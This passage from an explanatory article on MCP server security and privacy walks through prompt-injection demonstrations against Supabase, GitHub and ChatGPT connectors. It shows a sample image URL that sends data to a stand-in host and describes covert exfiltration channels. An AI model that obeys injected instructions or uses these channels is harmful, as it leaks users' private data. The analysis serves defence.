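Errico and colleagues write that current MCP servers typically offer all-or-nothing access, which makes it hard for a company to give employees different permissions. Their example is the official server for Snowflake, a data storage service, whose `execute_sql` tool accepts any query. They recommend building tools for specific uses instead. A tool that takes a supplier's name and returns unpaid invoices can answer Maya's question, and if the developer has written it correctly, it won't return salaries, whatever argument the model supplies.

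WunderGraph's server shows that finer divisions of access are practical. An agent needs separate scopes to connect, to see which tools exist, to call tools, and to use a particular tool. This means more work for the developer, who has to decide which scope each operation requires and keep those decisions up to date.

### Three messages out of 40,000

Answering Maya's question about Hartmann requires three messages: the invoice, a reminder, and the email in which Jo asks whether she ever paid. A program has to search all 40,000 messages to find them. How much private data is exposed depends on which program runs the search and what it can still read afterwards.

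With a mailbox-wide scope, the agent can read 39,997 messages that are irrelevant to the task, more than 99.99 per cent of the mailbox. If Maya receives 40 messages a day and the grant lasts a year, it will cover 54,600 messages by the end.

A server-side filter reduces what the model can reach. Suppose 60 of Maya's messages mention Hartmann, and the filter returns only those. A stricter filter on Hartmann's address would return fewer but would miss Jo's email, so a complete answer requires giving the model some messages it doesn't need. The model must not be able to change the filter. The `query` argument in Maya's original tool call doesn't meet this requirement, because the model wrote it and an injected instruction could make the model write a different one.

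Where the filter runs also matters. If the tool server applies it, the model can reach only 60 messages, but the server still holds a token for all 40,000. If the mail provider applies it, someone who breaks into the tool server can reach only the same 60 messages.

A short-lived grant limits how long an attacker can read the mailbox, but not how much they can copy in that time. At an assumed rate of 50 messages a second, an attacker could copy the whole mailbox in 800 seconds, before a 15-minute token expires. A five-minute token would still allow 15,000 messages to be copied. Short grants protect mail that arrives after they expire, and they make a token found in an old log useless. They do much less against an attack that happens while Maya is using the assistant.

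| Grant | Messages the model can reach | Messages someone with the tool server's token can reach | Access a year later |
|---|---|---|---|
| Whole mailbox for a year | 40,000, rising to 54,600 | 40,000, rising to 54,600 | Until Maya revokes it or it expires |
| Filter in the tool server, for a year | About 60, plus new matches | 40,000, rising to 54,600 | Until Maya revokes it or it expires |
| Filter at the provider, for a year | About 60, plus new matches | About 60, plus new matches | Until Maya revokes it or it expires |
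| Whole mailbox for 15 minutes | 40,000 | 40,000 | None |
| Filter at the provider, for 15 minutes | About 60 | About 60 | None |

The last option is the best, but Gmail's scopes don't support it. A host application can approximate it by running the search itself, showing Maya the matching subject lines, and passing the model only the messages she selects. The model then receives only three messages, but the tool server's token still gives access to the whole mailbox. None of these limits can retrieve a message that someone has already copied.

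### The Supabase demonstration

In 2025, the security company General Analysis demonstrated the risk of giving an agent far more read access than its task needs. The demonstration used Supabase's MCP server, which lets agents query the databases that Supabase hosts for software developers. *Supabase MCP can leak your entire SQL database* (Willison, 2025) quotes the researchers' account at length.

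The researchers imagined a company that kept its customer support tickets in a Supabase database. Such databases can use row-level security, a feature that attaches rules to a table and determines which rows each user can see. A rule for the tickets might look like this:

```sql
create policy own_tickets on support_tickets
  for select using (customer_id = auth.uid());
```

A customer who lists the table then gets only their own tickets, however they phrase the query. *When AI Has Root*, published by Pomerium, which sells access controls, describes the three roles in the demonstration. Customers could only create their own tickets and messages. Support staff could read and answer tickets but had no access to sensitive tables. The developer's agent ran in the code editor Cursor and connected as `service_role`, which is exempt from row-level security and could run any query on any table.

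The attack then went as follows:

1. The attacker, posing as a customer, filed a support ticket that contained instructions for an AI agent.
2. The database stored the ticket like any other. A member of the support staff could not have carried out the instructions even if they had wanted to.
3. The developer asked the agent to list the latest support tickets.
4. The agent read the ticket, followed the instructions and queried `integration_tokens`, a private table of access tokens for other services.
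5. It inserted the tokens into the ticket as a new message, and the attacker could read them on the ordinary support page.

The attacker only had to be able to file a ticket, and the attack never violated a database permission. The developer's request required only the tickets table. If the agent had used a role that could read only that table, the query in step 4 would have failed, even though the attack had fooled the model.

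*Systematization of Knowledge* (2025), a survey of MCP security, calls this an incident, but it was a demonstration. Supabase's *Defense in Depth for MCP Servers* (September 2025) stated that no customer had reported a data leak through MCP. A leak could have gone undetected, but there is no evidence of one. The survey notes that the query should have stood out in a log because no normal support task would read `integration_tokens`. That is also a good reason not to let the role read the table.

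Supabase also disputed the claim that MCP bypasses row-level security. It argued that the rules remained in force, though an MCP server may operate with higher privileges, as it did here. This is correct but makes little practical difference, because the rules allowed `service_role` to read everything.

Supabase's engineers had wrapped query results in warnings not to follow instructions in the data, and had experimented with classifiers to detect dangerous content. These measures reduced the risk but didn't eliminate it. The company conceded that people should never connect agents directly to production data, meaning the live database with real customers' records, and should use a development copy or anonymized records instead. It acknowledged that many of its users build directly on their live database, so they would have to change how they work to follow this advice.

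Supabase already recommended a read-only mode. According to its documentation for the server, this mode runs queries as a database user that cannot write, and switches off the tools that make changes. It would have stopped step 5, because the agent could not have added a message to the ticket. It would not necessarily have stopped step 4, and once the model has read the tokens, any other tool that can send data out could leak them. Willison considered the risk of even a read-only connection "enormous", and Supabase still ranked prompt injection as the main concern in that mode.

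A developer can also use project-scoped mode to limit the agent to one project, or feature groups to switch off whole sets of tools. Neither setting would have helped here, because the tickets and the tokens were in the same database and the agent reached both with the same tool. Supabase announced plans for access tokens with permissions for individual tools and data, and for an MCP server that would apply a project's existing row-level rules. Either could have prevented the leak if the developer had configured it for the support task.

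### How servers hold their credentials

Scopes can limit an agent's access only if its credential has them. Many tool servers instead use API keys, fixed strings that often grant all of the account's permissions. One reason, according to Trail of Bits' *Insecure credential storage plagues MCP* (2025), is that some services that people want to connect don't support OAuth, so the server has to ask for a long-term key.

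Skverer (2025), in *State of MCP Server Security 2025*, tried to measure how common this is. His team at Astrix, which sells tools for managing such credentials, searched GitHub for MCP servers, downloaded the README files of 5,205 repositories, and used a language model to classify the credentials each file mentioned. They found that 88 per cent of servers required credentials. About 53 per cent used API keys or personal access tokens, 8.5 per cent used OAuth, and 26.4 per cent mentioned credentials that the model could not classify. Among servers that took API keys, 79 per cent read them from environment variables.

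These figures are rough. The team reported that 30 per cent of the repositories it downloaded were not real MCP servers, so the sample was probably closer to 3,600 than to the 5,200 in the headline. The search favoured repositories with many stars, which may be better maintained than the rest. A README can also be out of date or leave out a login method. Skverer himself doubts the 88 per cent figure, because the language model sometimes misjudged whether a server needed credentials.

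The large group of unclassified servers affects the OAuth figure most. Without them, OAuth's share is about 14 per cent. Even if all of them used OAuth, which is unlikely, static keys would still be the most common type. So the main finding probably held in October 2025, but the survey is too old to show any effect of the July 2026 revision.

*Exposed by Design* (2026) audited 414 running MCP servers on the public internet and found that 380 (91.8 per cent) had no OAuth. Most either required no credential or accepted a fixed token, which was sometimes predictable or empty. Across a larger group of 640 servers, the study counted 687 tools that offered to run operating system commands without a login. The scopes on Maya's token would be irrelevant on such a server, because an attacker would not need a token.

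The two studies put OAuth use at 8.5 and 8.2 per cent, but the similarity is probably a coincidence. Skverer looked mainly at the credentials a server uses to reach another service, while *Exposed by Design* looked at the credentials a server requires from its callers. A server could use OAuth for one and not the other. Neither study weights its sample by how many people use each server.

The problem gets worse when several people share a credential. Errico and colleagues describe companies that give all employees the same token. The logs then attribute every action to one identity, and an intruder on any employee's computer gets the whole organization's access. Separate logins may not be enough. *A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers* (2026) cites earlier research that found servers commonly reuse a stored authorization without checking who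 is making the call. One employee's request could then run with another's permissions.

Trend Micro's *Beware of MCP Hardcoded Credentials* recommends credentials that come from the client, ideally an OAuth token kept in a secure store, over keys built into the server. Astrix released a tool that keeps keys out of configuration files by fetching them from such a store when a server starts. Skverer acknowledges that the tool does nothing about keys that grant too much access. For example, a server that fetches a key to Maya's whole mailbox can still read all of it.

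### Suitable read permissions

A sensible approach for most people is to give the assistant only the access it needs to be useful, expand that access for a particular task, and then remove the extra permissions. Login codes, access tokens and other data that could unlock other accounts deserve stricter treatment than ordinary private data, because one leak can expose much more than the message or table that contained them. If a service doesn't offer a suitable permission scope, the tool server or host application has to limit access.

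| Data | Permission to start with | When to widen it | What to keep out of reach |
|---|---|---|---|
| Mail | Headers for sorting; one label or a fixed search for questions about content | Read-only access to the mailbox for a search that Maya cannot narrow, ending with the task | Login codes and password-reset messages |
| Files | Files that Maya picks, or one folder | Read-only search of the whole store when she does not know where a document is | Identity documents, tax records and files containing keys |
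| Calendars | Free and busy times | Event details from one calendar for a limited period, for example to prepare for a meeting | Private calendars and those that colleagues have shared |
| Code | Read-only access to selected repositories | One more repository at a time, when the task needs it | Files containing keys, and private repositories during work on public bug reports |
| Databases | A read-only role limited to named tables in a development copy | Selected tables in the live database, with row-level rules that apply to the agent's role | Tables of passwords and tokens, and any role exempt from row-level rules |

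## Where personal data goes after a tool returns it

After Maya's mail server returns an email, her host application, its model provider and her other tool servers can all end up with copies. This can happen even if the mail server's permissions are narrow, nobody attacks her and the software works as its developers intended.

### The path of one email

Maya asked only how much she owes and when the payment is due. Suppose Jo's email asking whether Maya ever paid Hartmann also mentions that Jo is short of money after a hospital stay. When the model calls `read_message` to see whether the email helps, the tool returns all of it.

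The host application adds the text to the context. A language model ordinarily retains nothing between steps, so the application supplies the context again each time it runs the model. If the model makes four more tool calls before it answers, it processes Jo's email five times. It processes the email again whenever Maya asks another question in the same conversation, unless the application has removed it from the context.

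The model provider also stores some of what it receives. Anthropic logs the parameters and responses of tool calls. Google's *Gemini Apps Privacy Notice*, which covers its consumer assistant, lists information from connected apps and MCP servers, as well as the model's thinking steps, among the data Google collects. Jo's hospital stay could therefore be stored both in a tool result and in the model's thinking steps.

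If Maya has turned on a memory feature, part of the email may remain stored after the conversation ends. According to OpenAI's *Data sharing and privacy for apps in ChatGPT*, ChatGPT can create new memories from connected information when the source permits it, and can use that information to suggest prompts before the user asks anything. A saved memory that Jo has been ill could then influence an answer months later in a conversation unrelated to Hartmann.

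An employer may hold another copy of the data. On eligible ChatGPT Enterprise and Edu plans, authorized administrators can see records that may include the request sent to an app and information about its response. On the Business plan, administrators do not automatically get access to members' private conversations.

Text from the email can also be sent out in the arguments of later tool calls. If Maya asks the assistant to check Hartmann's new bank details, the model might search the web for the company's name, the invoice number and the amount. The search company would then learn about a debt Maya never meant to share with it. OpenAI confirms that conversation content may be used to write a web search, where the source allows one, and that a connected app may receive relevant conversation content and existing memories. An app may also receive the user's IP address and approximate location.

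Google warns users that Gemini can make mistakes such as "sharing your data with third parties unexpectedly". Errico and colleagues argue that such disclosures happen because agents treat all data as potentially useful for the task, without distinguishing what is sensitive.

### Why tools return more than the task needs

Maya's question has a two-part answer, an amount and a date. But the developer of a mail tool cannot know whether the next user will want the date, the sender's address or the third paragraph. The easiest design is to return the provider's whole record and let the model find what it needs. For Hartmann's invoice, that record might look like this:

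```json
{
  "from": "billing@hartmann.example",
  "to": ["maya@example.com"],
  "cc": ["r.osei@hartmann.example", "jo@example.com"],
  "subject": "Re: Re: Invoice 2291",
  "body": "480 euros, due 30 November. [11 earlier messages quoted below]",
  "attachments": ["invoice-2291.pdf", "all-open-accounts.xlsx"]
}
```

The answer takes up less than one line of the tool's output. The rest includes two other people's addresses, a long correspondence and a spreadsheet that a clerk probably attached by accident.

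Email threads are especially wasteful because replies usually quote the messages before them. If a thread has n messages and every reply quotes all the earlier ones, a tool that returns the whole thread returns this many message texts:

1 + 2 + ... + n = n(n + 1) / 2

Each reply in Hartmann's thread of 12 messages quotes all the earlier ones, so returning the whole thread returns 78 message texts, including duplicates. Returning only the newest message would remove the duplicates but still include the text of all 12, so the tool also has to strip the quoted text.

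Other kinds of data can also include more personal information than the task needs. A calendar event can contain the guests' addresses and the password for a video call when the user only wanted to know when she was free. A customer record can include a date of birth and years of support notes when the agent only needed a delivery address.

### People who never agreed to the connection

Jo and the clerk at Hartmann chose to send Maya a message and an invoice. Neither agreed to let an AI company process what they wrote, because only Maya saw the consent screen. She can read the provider's terms and change her settings, but Jo has no setting that controls how the provider handles the message.

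Providers acknowledge that they handle personal data about people other than the user. In its privacy documentation for users in the European Union and the United Kingdom, Google gives the example of a user who asks Gemini to summarize an email from a named contact. Google processes the contact's personal data on the basis of legitimate interests, a legal ground that does not require the contact's consent. Anthropic likewise acknowledges in its *Model training notice* that its services may incidentally process the personal data of people who are not registered users, and that those people may have privacy rights.

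Google's *About personalization with Connected Apps* explains that Gemini uses connected data beyond answering a single question, to draw conclusions about the user's relationships and the "people in your world". The data may concern race, religion or health. With Google Photos, depending on the user's settings, Gemini may associate the user's face with places and times to infer where they have been.

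European law may let a person object to such processing or have false information corrected, and Google provides a form for both requests. But Jo would first have to know that Maya had connected her own mailbox, and the OAuth flow would not notify Jo.

### Training and retention on personal accounts

Anthropic, OpenAI and Google all say they do not simply train their models on a connected mailbox, but their exceptions differ. The most important exceptions concern text that has passed from the mailbox into the conversation.

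Anthropic excludes raw content from connectors, including local and remote MCP servers, from the data it may use to improve its models, though it may include content that someone copies directly into the conversation. If a user has allowed training, Anthropic may use the entire related conversation, which appears to include any answer in which Claude restates an email's contents. Anthropic may also analyse conversations flagged for safety review and use them to train the models its safety team works with.

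Under Anthropic's *Updates to our consumer terms*, the company keeps data for five years if the user allows training and for 30 days otherwise. The five-year period also covers feedback on Claude's answers, so a single rating can extend how long Anthropic keeps the text it concerns.

OpenAI has a specific rule for Gmail, Google Drive and other connected Google apps. It does not train its general models on data taken directly from them, or on anything derived from that data, with three exceptions:

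- conversations that the user submits as feedback, for example with a thumbs-up
- material that the user copies, pastes or uploads into the conversation
- material that ChatGPT includes in its response

The last exception covers much ordinary use, since people connect a mailbox to get answers about its contents. If ChatGPT tells Maya that she owes Hartmann 480 euros, OpenAI may train on that sentence, though not on the email itself. She can prevent this by turning off "Improve the model for everyone", which stops OpenAI from training on app data even when it appears in her conversations.

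Google trains on more of the connected data. It trains Gemini on the summaries, excerpts and inferences that Gemini produces from relevant emails and files, though not directly on a user's whole Gmail inbox. Google acknowledges that if an email is short or especially relevant, "the summary may just be the email". Google's announcement of the feature, *Gemini introduces Personal Intelligence*, described the training data as "limited info, like specific prompts". Readers of the announcement probably would not have guessed that this could include a complete email.

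Gemini users with personal accounts can stop this training by turning off a setting called Keep Activity, but Google does not let them connect Gmail or Drive while it is off. Google deletes saved activity after 18 months by default, and users can change this to 3 months, 36 months or never.

The terms also depend on where someone uses the assistant. Gemini features built into Gmail and Google Docs have their own privacy commitments. But a user with a personal account can also share the same emails with the Gemini app, or with Search for personalization. In those cases, Google's *Learn how Gemini in Gmail, Calendar, Chat, Docs, Drive, Sheets, Slides, Meet* refers users to the terms of those services, which allow training. In the United States, users can connect Gmail to Search, which gives all of Google's Search services, including Maps, Shopping and Translate, access to their Gmail data.

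### Terms for business accounts

Business accounts have stronger protection against training. Anthropic does not use data from its Team and Enterprise plans to train models. By default, OpenAI does not train on data from Business, Enterprise and Edu workspaces. Google's terms, updated in October 2026, require permission before a business customer's content is used to train generative AI outside that customer's organization.

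| Provider | Training on connected data, personal account | Retention, personal account | Training, business account |
|---|---|---|---|
| Anthropic | Not on raw connector content, but possibly on what someone copies into the conversation | 30-day period, or five years if the user allows training | No |
| OpenAI, for Google apps | Only on feedback, material the user adds and material in ChatGPT's response | Up to 30 days after the user deletes a chat, with exceptions for security, legal duties and de-identified chats | Not by default |
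| Google, for Gemini | On summaries, excerpts and inferences, sometimes a whole email | 18 months by default, and up to three years for reviewed chats | Not outside the customer's organization without permission |

These are contractual promises about how each company handles the data it receives, and they do not reduce how much text it receives. They also depend on the account, so an employee who connects a work document to an AI assistant through her personal account loses the protection her employer negotiated.

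### Human review and Google's warning

People as well as models may read data from connected apps. On personal accounts, Google has human reviewers, some from outside companies, examine some of the connected-app data that Gemini processes. They see prompts and answers, along with summaries and excerpts of emails and files. Before review, Google takes steps such as separating this material from the user's account and reducing the personal information in it, except when it is dealing with abuse or harm. If the user has submitted feedback, reviewers may also see some of the inbox itself.

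Removing Maya's name from Jo's email might not hide who wrote it, because the text might still mention Jo, Hartmann and the hospital, and someone who knew them could identify the writer from those details.

When Google first connected its assistant, then called Bard, to Gmail, Docs and Drive, it promised that human reviewers would not see content from those services and that it would not use the content to train Bard (Pinsky, 2023, *Bard can now connect to your Google apps and services*). O'Shei's blog post of 10 November 2026, *Google opens consumer Drive and email to human review*, claims that Google has quietly reversed its promise about human review. Google now asks people not to connect apps containing confidential information "that you wouldn't want a reviewer to see".

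The reversal is older than the blog post suggests. An April 2026 copy of Google's help page for Search already contains the warning, and so does a June copy of the corresponding page for Gemini.

O'Shei also claims that casual questions can trigger searches of a user's files even if the user doesn't name Gmail or Drive. Google's documentation partly supports this. For the basic Workspace connection, Google tells users to mention the service, or something like "email" or "documents", at the start of each new conversation. But in Google's example of personalization, a user asks for a list of restaurants for a trip without mentioning email, and Gemini may then look through their emails for the hotel and flight. O'Shei's claim that automated filters routinely miss details such as reservation codes is plausible, but his post includes no measurements.

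OpenAI's two help pages on connected data do not discuss human reviewers, so they do not rule out employees reading conversations. For business customers, an April 2025 version of Google's terms barred human review without permission.

### What revoking access leaves behind

If Maya disconnects her mailbox, the assistant can no longer fetch messages through that connection, but anything it has already fetched is not deleted. The mailbox is still worth disconnecting as soon as she no longer needs the connection.

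| What Maya does | What it stops | What can remain |
|---|---|---|
| Disconnects her mailbox | New reads through that connection | Chats, memories, saved files and logs |
| Deletes an email from the mailbox | Later searches that would have found it | Copies in chats and activity records |
| Turns off memory | Use of saved memories in new answers | The connection itself and earlier chats |
| Deletes a chat | Access to it from her history | Memories drawn from it, and copies that other services received |

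OpenAI has separate controls for Memory and connected apps, so turning off Memory leaves apps connected. Disconnecting an app does not remove chats or memories. If an employer has set up a shared index of its Google Drive files, that index remains after an employee disconnects her own account.

After a user deletes an email, Gemini's answers may not reflect the change for days. Google keeps chats that human reviewers have examined for up to three years, even if the user deletes all her activity, because it stores them separately from her account. If she turns Keep Activity off and on again, Google restores access to the apps she had connected before. To prevent this, she has to disconnect each app.

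Anthropic will not use a deleted conversation in future training, but deletion does not change a model already trained on it. Deletion also does not remove data the model has sent to other tool servers. If the model included Jo's words in a call to Maya's issue tracker, the tracker's operator keeps them under its own terms.

Maya should therefore disconnect the mailbox first, so that the assistant cannot fetch the same messages again, and then delete the relevant chats, memories and activity records. She would have to ask the operators of other tool servers separately to delete her data, if she can work out which ones received it.

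### How a tool server can return less

A tool server can prevent these copies more reliably than a user can delete them, because the model provider never receives the text that the server leaves out. The developer can start by returning only selected fields. For a question about invoices, Maya's mail server could reduce the record above to this:

```json
{
  "message_id": "m-20931",
  "from": "billing@hartmann.example",
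  "amount_due": "480 euros",
  "due_date": "30 November",
  "attachment_count": 2
}
```

The model can answer from these fields and request the full message if they aren't enough. This works well for databases and calendars, where the fields already exist. With an email, the server has to extract the amount from prose and may pick the wrong figure. A simpler option is for the server to strip quoted replies and signatures and return attachments only on request.

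Redaction removes sensitive details from the text the server returns. A program can recognize most card numbers and phone numbers by their format and replace each with a placeholder. The server can keep the real value and insert it in a later call, so the model can arrange a payment to Hartmann without seeing the bank account number. But Jo's sentence about the hospital has no recognizable format, and a filter strict enough to catch every such sentence would probably also remove text that Maya needs.

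A cap on results limits how much one careless search can expose. The server has to enforce the cap, because the model could raise the `limit` in Maya's original call from 2 to 500. Even with a maximum of ten messages per call, an agent could read all 40,000 in 4,000 calls, so the server also needs a cap on the total per conversation or day. When the agent reaches it, the server can ask Maya whether to continue.

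Finally, the server should not keep what it returns. It needs the text of an email only while it answers the call, and any temporary copy can expire within minutes. Its logs can record the time, the tool and the message identifiers without the contents. After an incident, an investigator can use the identifiers to find the messages in Maya's mailbox, provided she hasn't deleted them. Search terms need similar care, because a search for a clinic's name can reveal as much as the email it finds.

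## How instructions in retrieved content misdirect the agent

Someone could send Maya an email that, unlike Jo's, contains instructions for her assistant. This is called indirect prompt injection, and researchers have repeatedly used it to show how an outsider can take private data from an account without logging in to it.

### The steps of an attack

In an earlier example, a bug report led Maya's agent to quote one of her contracts in a public comment. That attack took five steps, and each depended on a different condition:

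| Step | What makes it possible | What would prevent it |
|---|---|---|
| An outsider writes text where the agent will read it | A place that accepts text from strangers, such as an inbox, an issue tracker or a web page | Accepting reports only from people Maya knows |
| Maya makes an ordinary request | A request broad enough to retrieve the text | A request about one particular report |
| The text enters the context | A tool that returns the whole report | A tool that returns only dates and report numbers |
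| The agent reads private data | A model that follows the text, and a token that covers the contract | A model that ignores the text, or a token without access to contracts |
| An outbound channel carries the data away | An action whose result the attacker can see | No such action, or Maya's refusal to approve it |

The attacker performs only the first step, and Maya and her agent do the rest in the course of normal work. The attacker does not have to know when she will ask about her bug reports, because the text can stay on the tracker until she does. The attacker also does not need the names of her tools, since the model has the tool descriptions and can use them to choose the call that would fetch a contract. Sending the same text to a thousand people takes little more effort than sending it to one, so even an attack that usually fails may be worth trying.

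Maya's request affects how much hostile text can reach the model. She gets 40 messages a day, so summarizing the past week's mail puts about 280 in the context, and one hostile message is enough to misdirect the agent. If she asks about Hartmann, the search returns only messages that mention the company. An attacker would then have to guess the name of one of her suppliers, which is harder unless Hartmann lists its customers on its website.

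Sometimes the private data is already in the context when the hostile text arrives. If Maya discussed her tax return with the agent earlier in the conversation, the agent can leak those details without opening any file, as long as it has a way to send them.

### The lethal trifecta

Willison (2025) argues in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* that an attacker can steal data from an agent that combines access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. The untrusted content brings the attacker's text into the agent's context, access to private data lets the agent read what the attacker wants, and external communication lets the agent send it out.

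Willison, who coined the term "prompt injection" in 2022, wrote this for people who combine tools themselves. He lists 17 cases since April 2023 of this kind of attack affecting released products, including ChatGPT, Slack and Microsoft Copilot. The vendors promptly fixed almost all of them, usually by closing the channel the data left through. But a vendor cannot do this for a user who combines one developer's mail server with another's web tool.

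The list explains well how outside text leads to data theft. An attacker gains nothing of value if the agent has no private data, cannot reach the model if the agent reads no untrusted content, and cannot get the data out if the agent has no external communication. Users can apply the list without knowing how language models work.

This rule is hard to apply because one connection can supply several of the conditions. A mailbox holds private data, and most of the text in it comes from other people. If the mail server also offers `send_message`, the agent has a way to send data out, so the one connection supplies all three conditions. Maya can't remove the untrusted content without removing most of her mail. Limiting the agent to headers leaves it much less to disclose, but it would still read subject lines written by strangers.

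A user with no connected accounts may also meet all three conditions. Tenable's *HackedGPT* describes seven weaknesses in ChatGPT that could expose a user's saved memories and chat history, in some cases after the user only asked a question. Memories and old chats are private data, and web search can supply both the untrusted text and a way to send the data out. Tenable reported the weaknesses as its own researchers' findings, and no real victims are known.

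An attack can fail even when all three conditions are met, because the model may ignore the instructions or the user may refuse a confirmation prompt. Willison accepts that models behave differently from one run to the next and that developers can make them less likely to obey. But he argues that nobody can be confident their efforts will work every time, because an attacker can phrase the instructions in endless ways. He therefore advises users to avoid the combination altogether. That is sound advice for a tax archive, but it would rule out many of the tasks for which people connect a mailbox.

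### The GitHub demonstration

GitHub's official MCP server met all three conditions by itself. Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (26 May 2025) describes how the company's researchers used the server to extract private information about a demonstration user.

The user's account had a public repository, or project folder, with the code of a simple Pacman game. It also had several private repositories with personal projects and sensitive information. The agent ran in the host application Claude Desktop, used the model Claude 4 Opus, and could reach all of them through the same server. The attack went as follows:

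1. The researchers filed an issue on the Pacman repository. An issue is GitHub's term for a bug report or request, and anyone with an account can file one on a public repository. It contained instructions for an AI agent.
2. The user made a harmless request. According to the researchers, "Have a look at the open issues" is enough.
3. The agent went through the issues until it came to the hostile one.
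4. It followed the instructions and read data from the private repositories.
5. It opened a pull request, which is a proposed change to a project's files, on the Pacman repository and included the private data.

Anyone could read the pull request, which disclosed information about the user's private repositories, including one called Jupiter Star, along with the user's salary and plan to move to South America. The data came from the demonstration account, and Invariant Labs does not report an attack on a real user.

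By default, Claude Desktop asks the user to confirm each tool call, so an attentive user could have stopped the agent from reading the private repositories or creating the pull request. The researchers observe that many people choose "Always Allow" and stop watching individual actions.

Invariant Labs says GitHub alone cannot solve the problem by patching the server. The server's code had no flaw. It returned a public issue to someone entitled to read it, returned private files to an agent acting for their owner, and opened a pull request with the owner's permission. The tools were also intact, unlike in tool poisoning, where an attacker hides instructions in a tool description. The leak resulted from the sequence of calls, each correct on its own, so Invariant Labs argues that the fix must cover the whole agent. It tested only Claude Desktop but expects any agent that uses the server to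 be vulnerable, whatever its model.

They are right about the cause, but the claim is a little too strong for this attack. All the calls went through one server, so GitHub could make that server stop a user's agent from opening a public pull request after it has read a private repository. The server could also withhold issues written by people who have no role in the project. Either change would have blocked this attack, but also some legitimate work. Neither would help if the agent read the issue on GitHub and then leaked a file through a mail server, because only the first call would go through GitHub's server.

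The company sells the kind of agent monitoring it recommends, including a rule that limits an agent to one repository per session. A token that covers only the public repository would give much of the same protection. In the Supabase demonstration, a narrower database role would have had a similar effect.

The researchers called their injection "relatively simplistic" and said many ready-made detectors missed it. One successful attack on Claude 4 Opus, a new model at the time, shows that the sequence can work, but not how often current models would follow the same text.

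### A mail attack that needs no click

ShadowLeak, an attack that the security company Radware published on 18 September 2025, began with an email. It targeted Deep Research, a ChatGPT feature that reads many sources on its own and writes a report. Users could connect it to Gmail.

The attacker hid instructions in the email's formatting. Infosecurity Magazine's *Zero-Click Vulnerability in ChatGPT's Agent Enables Silent Gmail Data Theft* describes white text on a white background and microscopic fonts, which a person would not notice but the model would receive as ordinary text. The victim then had to give the agent a task that involved reading the message, such as summarizing the past few days' emails, the example in heise online's *ShadowLeak*. The agent found the instructions, followed them and sent data out by opening a web address that contained it, as The Decoder explains.

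Security researchers call such an attack "zero-click" because the victim does not have to open the email, follow a link or download a file. But this attack could only work after the victim asked ChatGPT to use Deep Research with the mailbox, so someone who had connected Gmail but never used it with Deep Research was not at risk.

ShadowLeak used OpenAI's own Gmail connector, not an MCP server that the victim had added. An MCP mail server that returned the same email to an agent with web access would create the same conditions for the attack.

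OpenAI's cloud sent the request that carried the data, so a company monitoring its own network and laptops would not have seen the data leave. Radware's researchers said there was no evidence that attackers had exploited the weakness, according to Insurance Journal's *OpenAI Fixed ChatGPT Security Flaw That Put Gmail Data at Risk* (2025). This is less reassuring than it would be if the attack left traces on the victim's computer, because OpenAI holds the most useful records.

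Radware reported ShadowLeak on 18 June 2025. OpenAI patched it in early August and confirmed the fix on 3 September. Radware soon found further weaknesses, described in its *ZombieAgent*, that could leak data from accounts connected to ChatGPT, including Gmail and Outlook. The attacks again used OpenAI's connectors, according to eWeek's *A ‘Zombie’ AI Attack Shows How ChatGPT Can Leak Your Secrets*. A hostile email could take effect as soon as the user asked ChatGPT to do something in Gmail, and the data again left through OpenAI's servers. In another version, the user had to share a malicious file with ChatGPT.

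According to Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data*, OpenAI received the ZombieAgent report in September 2025 and fixed the weaknesses in mid-December. This attack was also a demonstration, with no known victims. The fix took about three months, compared with roughly six weeks for ShadowLeak, so users cannot count on a vendor to fix such weaknesses within days.

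### Outbound channels that do not look like sending

Maya would recognize `send_message` as an outbound channel and might refuse to connect it, but other outbound channels look like reading, searching or formatting an answer. Willison points out that any tool that can make a web request can pass stolen data to an attacker, whether the request calls an API, loads an image or opens a link the user clicks.

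An image works as a channel because a program has to request it from an address, and whoever writes the address can put data in it. An injected instruction might lead the model to include an image with this address in its answer:

```text
https://images.example/logo.png?d=hartmann-480-euros
```

If Maya's host application loads images automatically, it requests this address as soon as it displays the answer. The server logs the address, and its owner can then read the text after the question mark. Maya sees a logo, or nothing if the image is a single transparent pixel.

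| Channel | How the data leaves | Who can read it | What Maya has to do |
|---|---|---|---|
| Image in an answer | The host application requests an address that contains the data | The owner of the image's server | Nothing, if images load automatically |
| Link in an answer | The address behind the link contains the data | The owner of the linked site | Click it, or paste it into a program that fetches a preview |
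| Web page that the agent opens | The agent requests an address that contains the data | The owner of the site | Nothing |
| Search query | The agent includes private details in its search terms | The search company, or the owner of a site with its own search page | Nothing |
| Public comment or pull request | The agent posts the data as text | Anyone | Nothing, unless the host application asks for approval |
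| Calendar invitation | The event's title or description contains the data | Everyone the agent invites | Nothing, unless the host application asks for approval |

A search query is the weakest of these channels for an attacker, who normally can't see what people type into a large search engine. But an attacker who runs the search tool or the website that the agent searches can use queries to steal data.

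The connection that lets Maya's agent read bug reports in her issue tracker also lets it post public comments there. This is easy to overlook because she may think of the tracker only as a place the agent reads from.

An agent can leak private data through a channel that carries very little information at a time. If it can open ten fixed web addresses, one for each digit, it can reveal a six-digit login code from Maya's mailbox in six requests. The attacker reads the code from the order in which the requests arrive. A filter that checks addresses for private text would miss the leak because none of the addresses contains any.

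### The storage that ChatGPT accounts shared

Maya could check every channel in that table and still miss one inside the provider's systems. Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) describes a hidden path to the public internet from the isolated environment where ChatGPT runs code. A single malicious prompt could make ChatGPT send a user's messages and uploaded files over this path without the user's approval. OpenAI closed the path on 20 February 2026, and The Hacker News (2026) reported no evidence of malicious use.

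In June 2026, Check Point Research found a channel between ChatGPT accounts, according to CNews' *Чужую почту в Gmail можно читать с помощью ChatGPT* (2026). The group published the finding on 8 September as *The Shared Clipboard Inside the Sandbox*, by Alexey Bukhteyev.

ChatGPT runs code in a container, an isolated environment that belongs to one user's session. The containers could not reach the internet directly or communicate with each other. But code often needs software packages, so OpenAI let all the containers download them from the same internal storage service, JFrog Artifactory.

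The service let users attach to a stored file properties, which are short named notes such as a version or a status. The containers needed only to read packages, but IlSoftware.it's *ChatGPT, un canale nascosto permetteva di sottrarre dati tra account* explains that their credentials also let them write some of these properties. The researchers wrote a test value from one account and read it from another. They could split longer data into pieces and reassemble it in the second account.

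This gave two accounts a place to exchange messages, but the victim's session had no reason to look there. The attacker first had to get an instruction into that session. The victim might open a conversation that the attacker had shared and send an ordinary message in it, paste in a prompt that the attacker had written, or use a custom GPT, a version of ChatGPT that another user has configured, with a hidden instruction. The attack then worked like this:

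1. From their own account, the attacker wrote a task into the shared storage.
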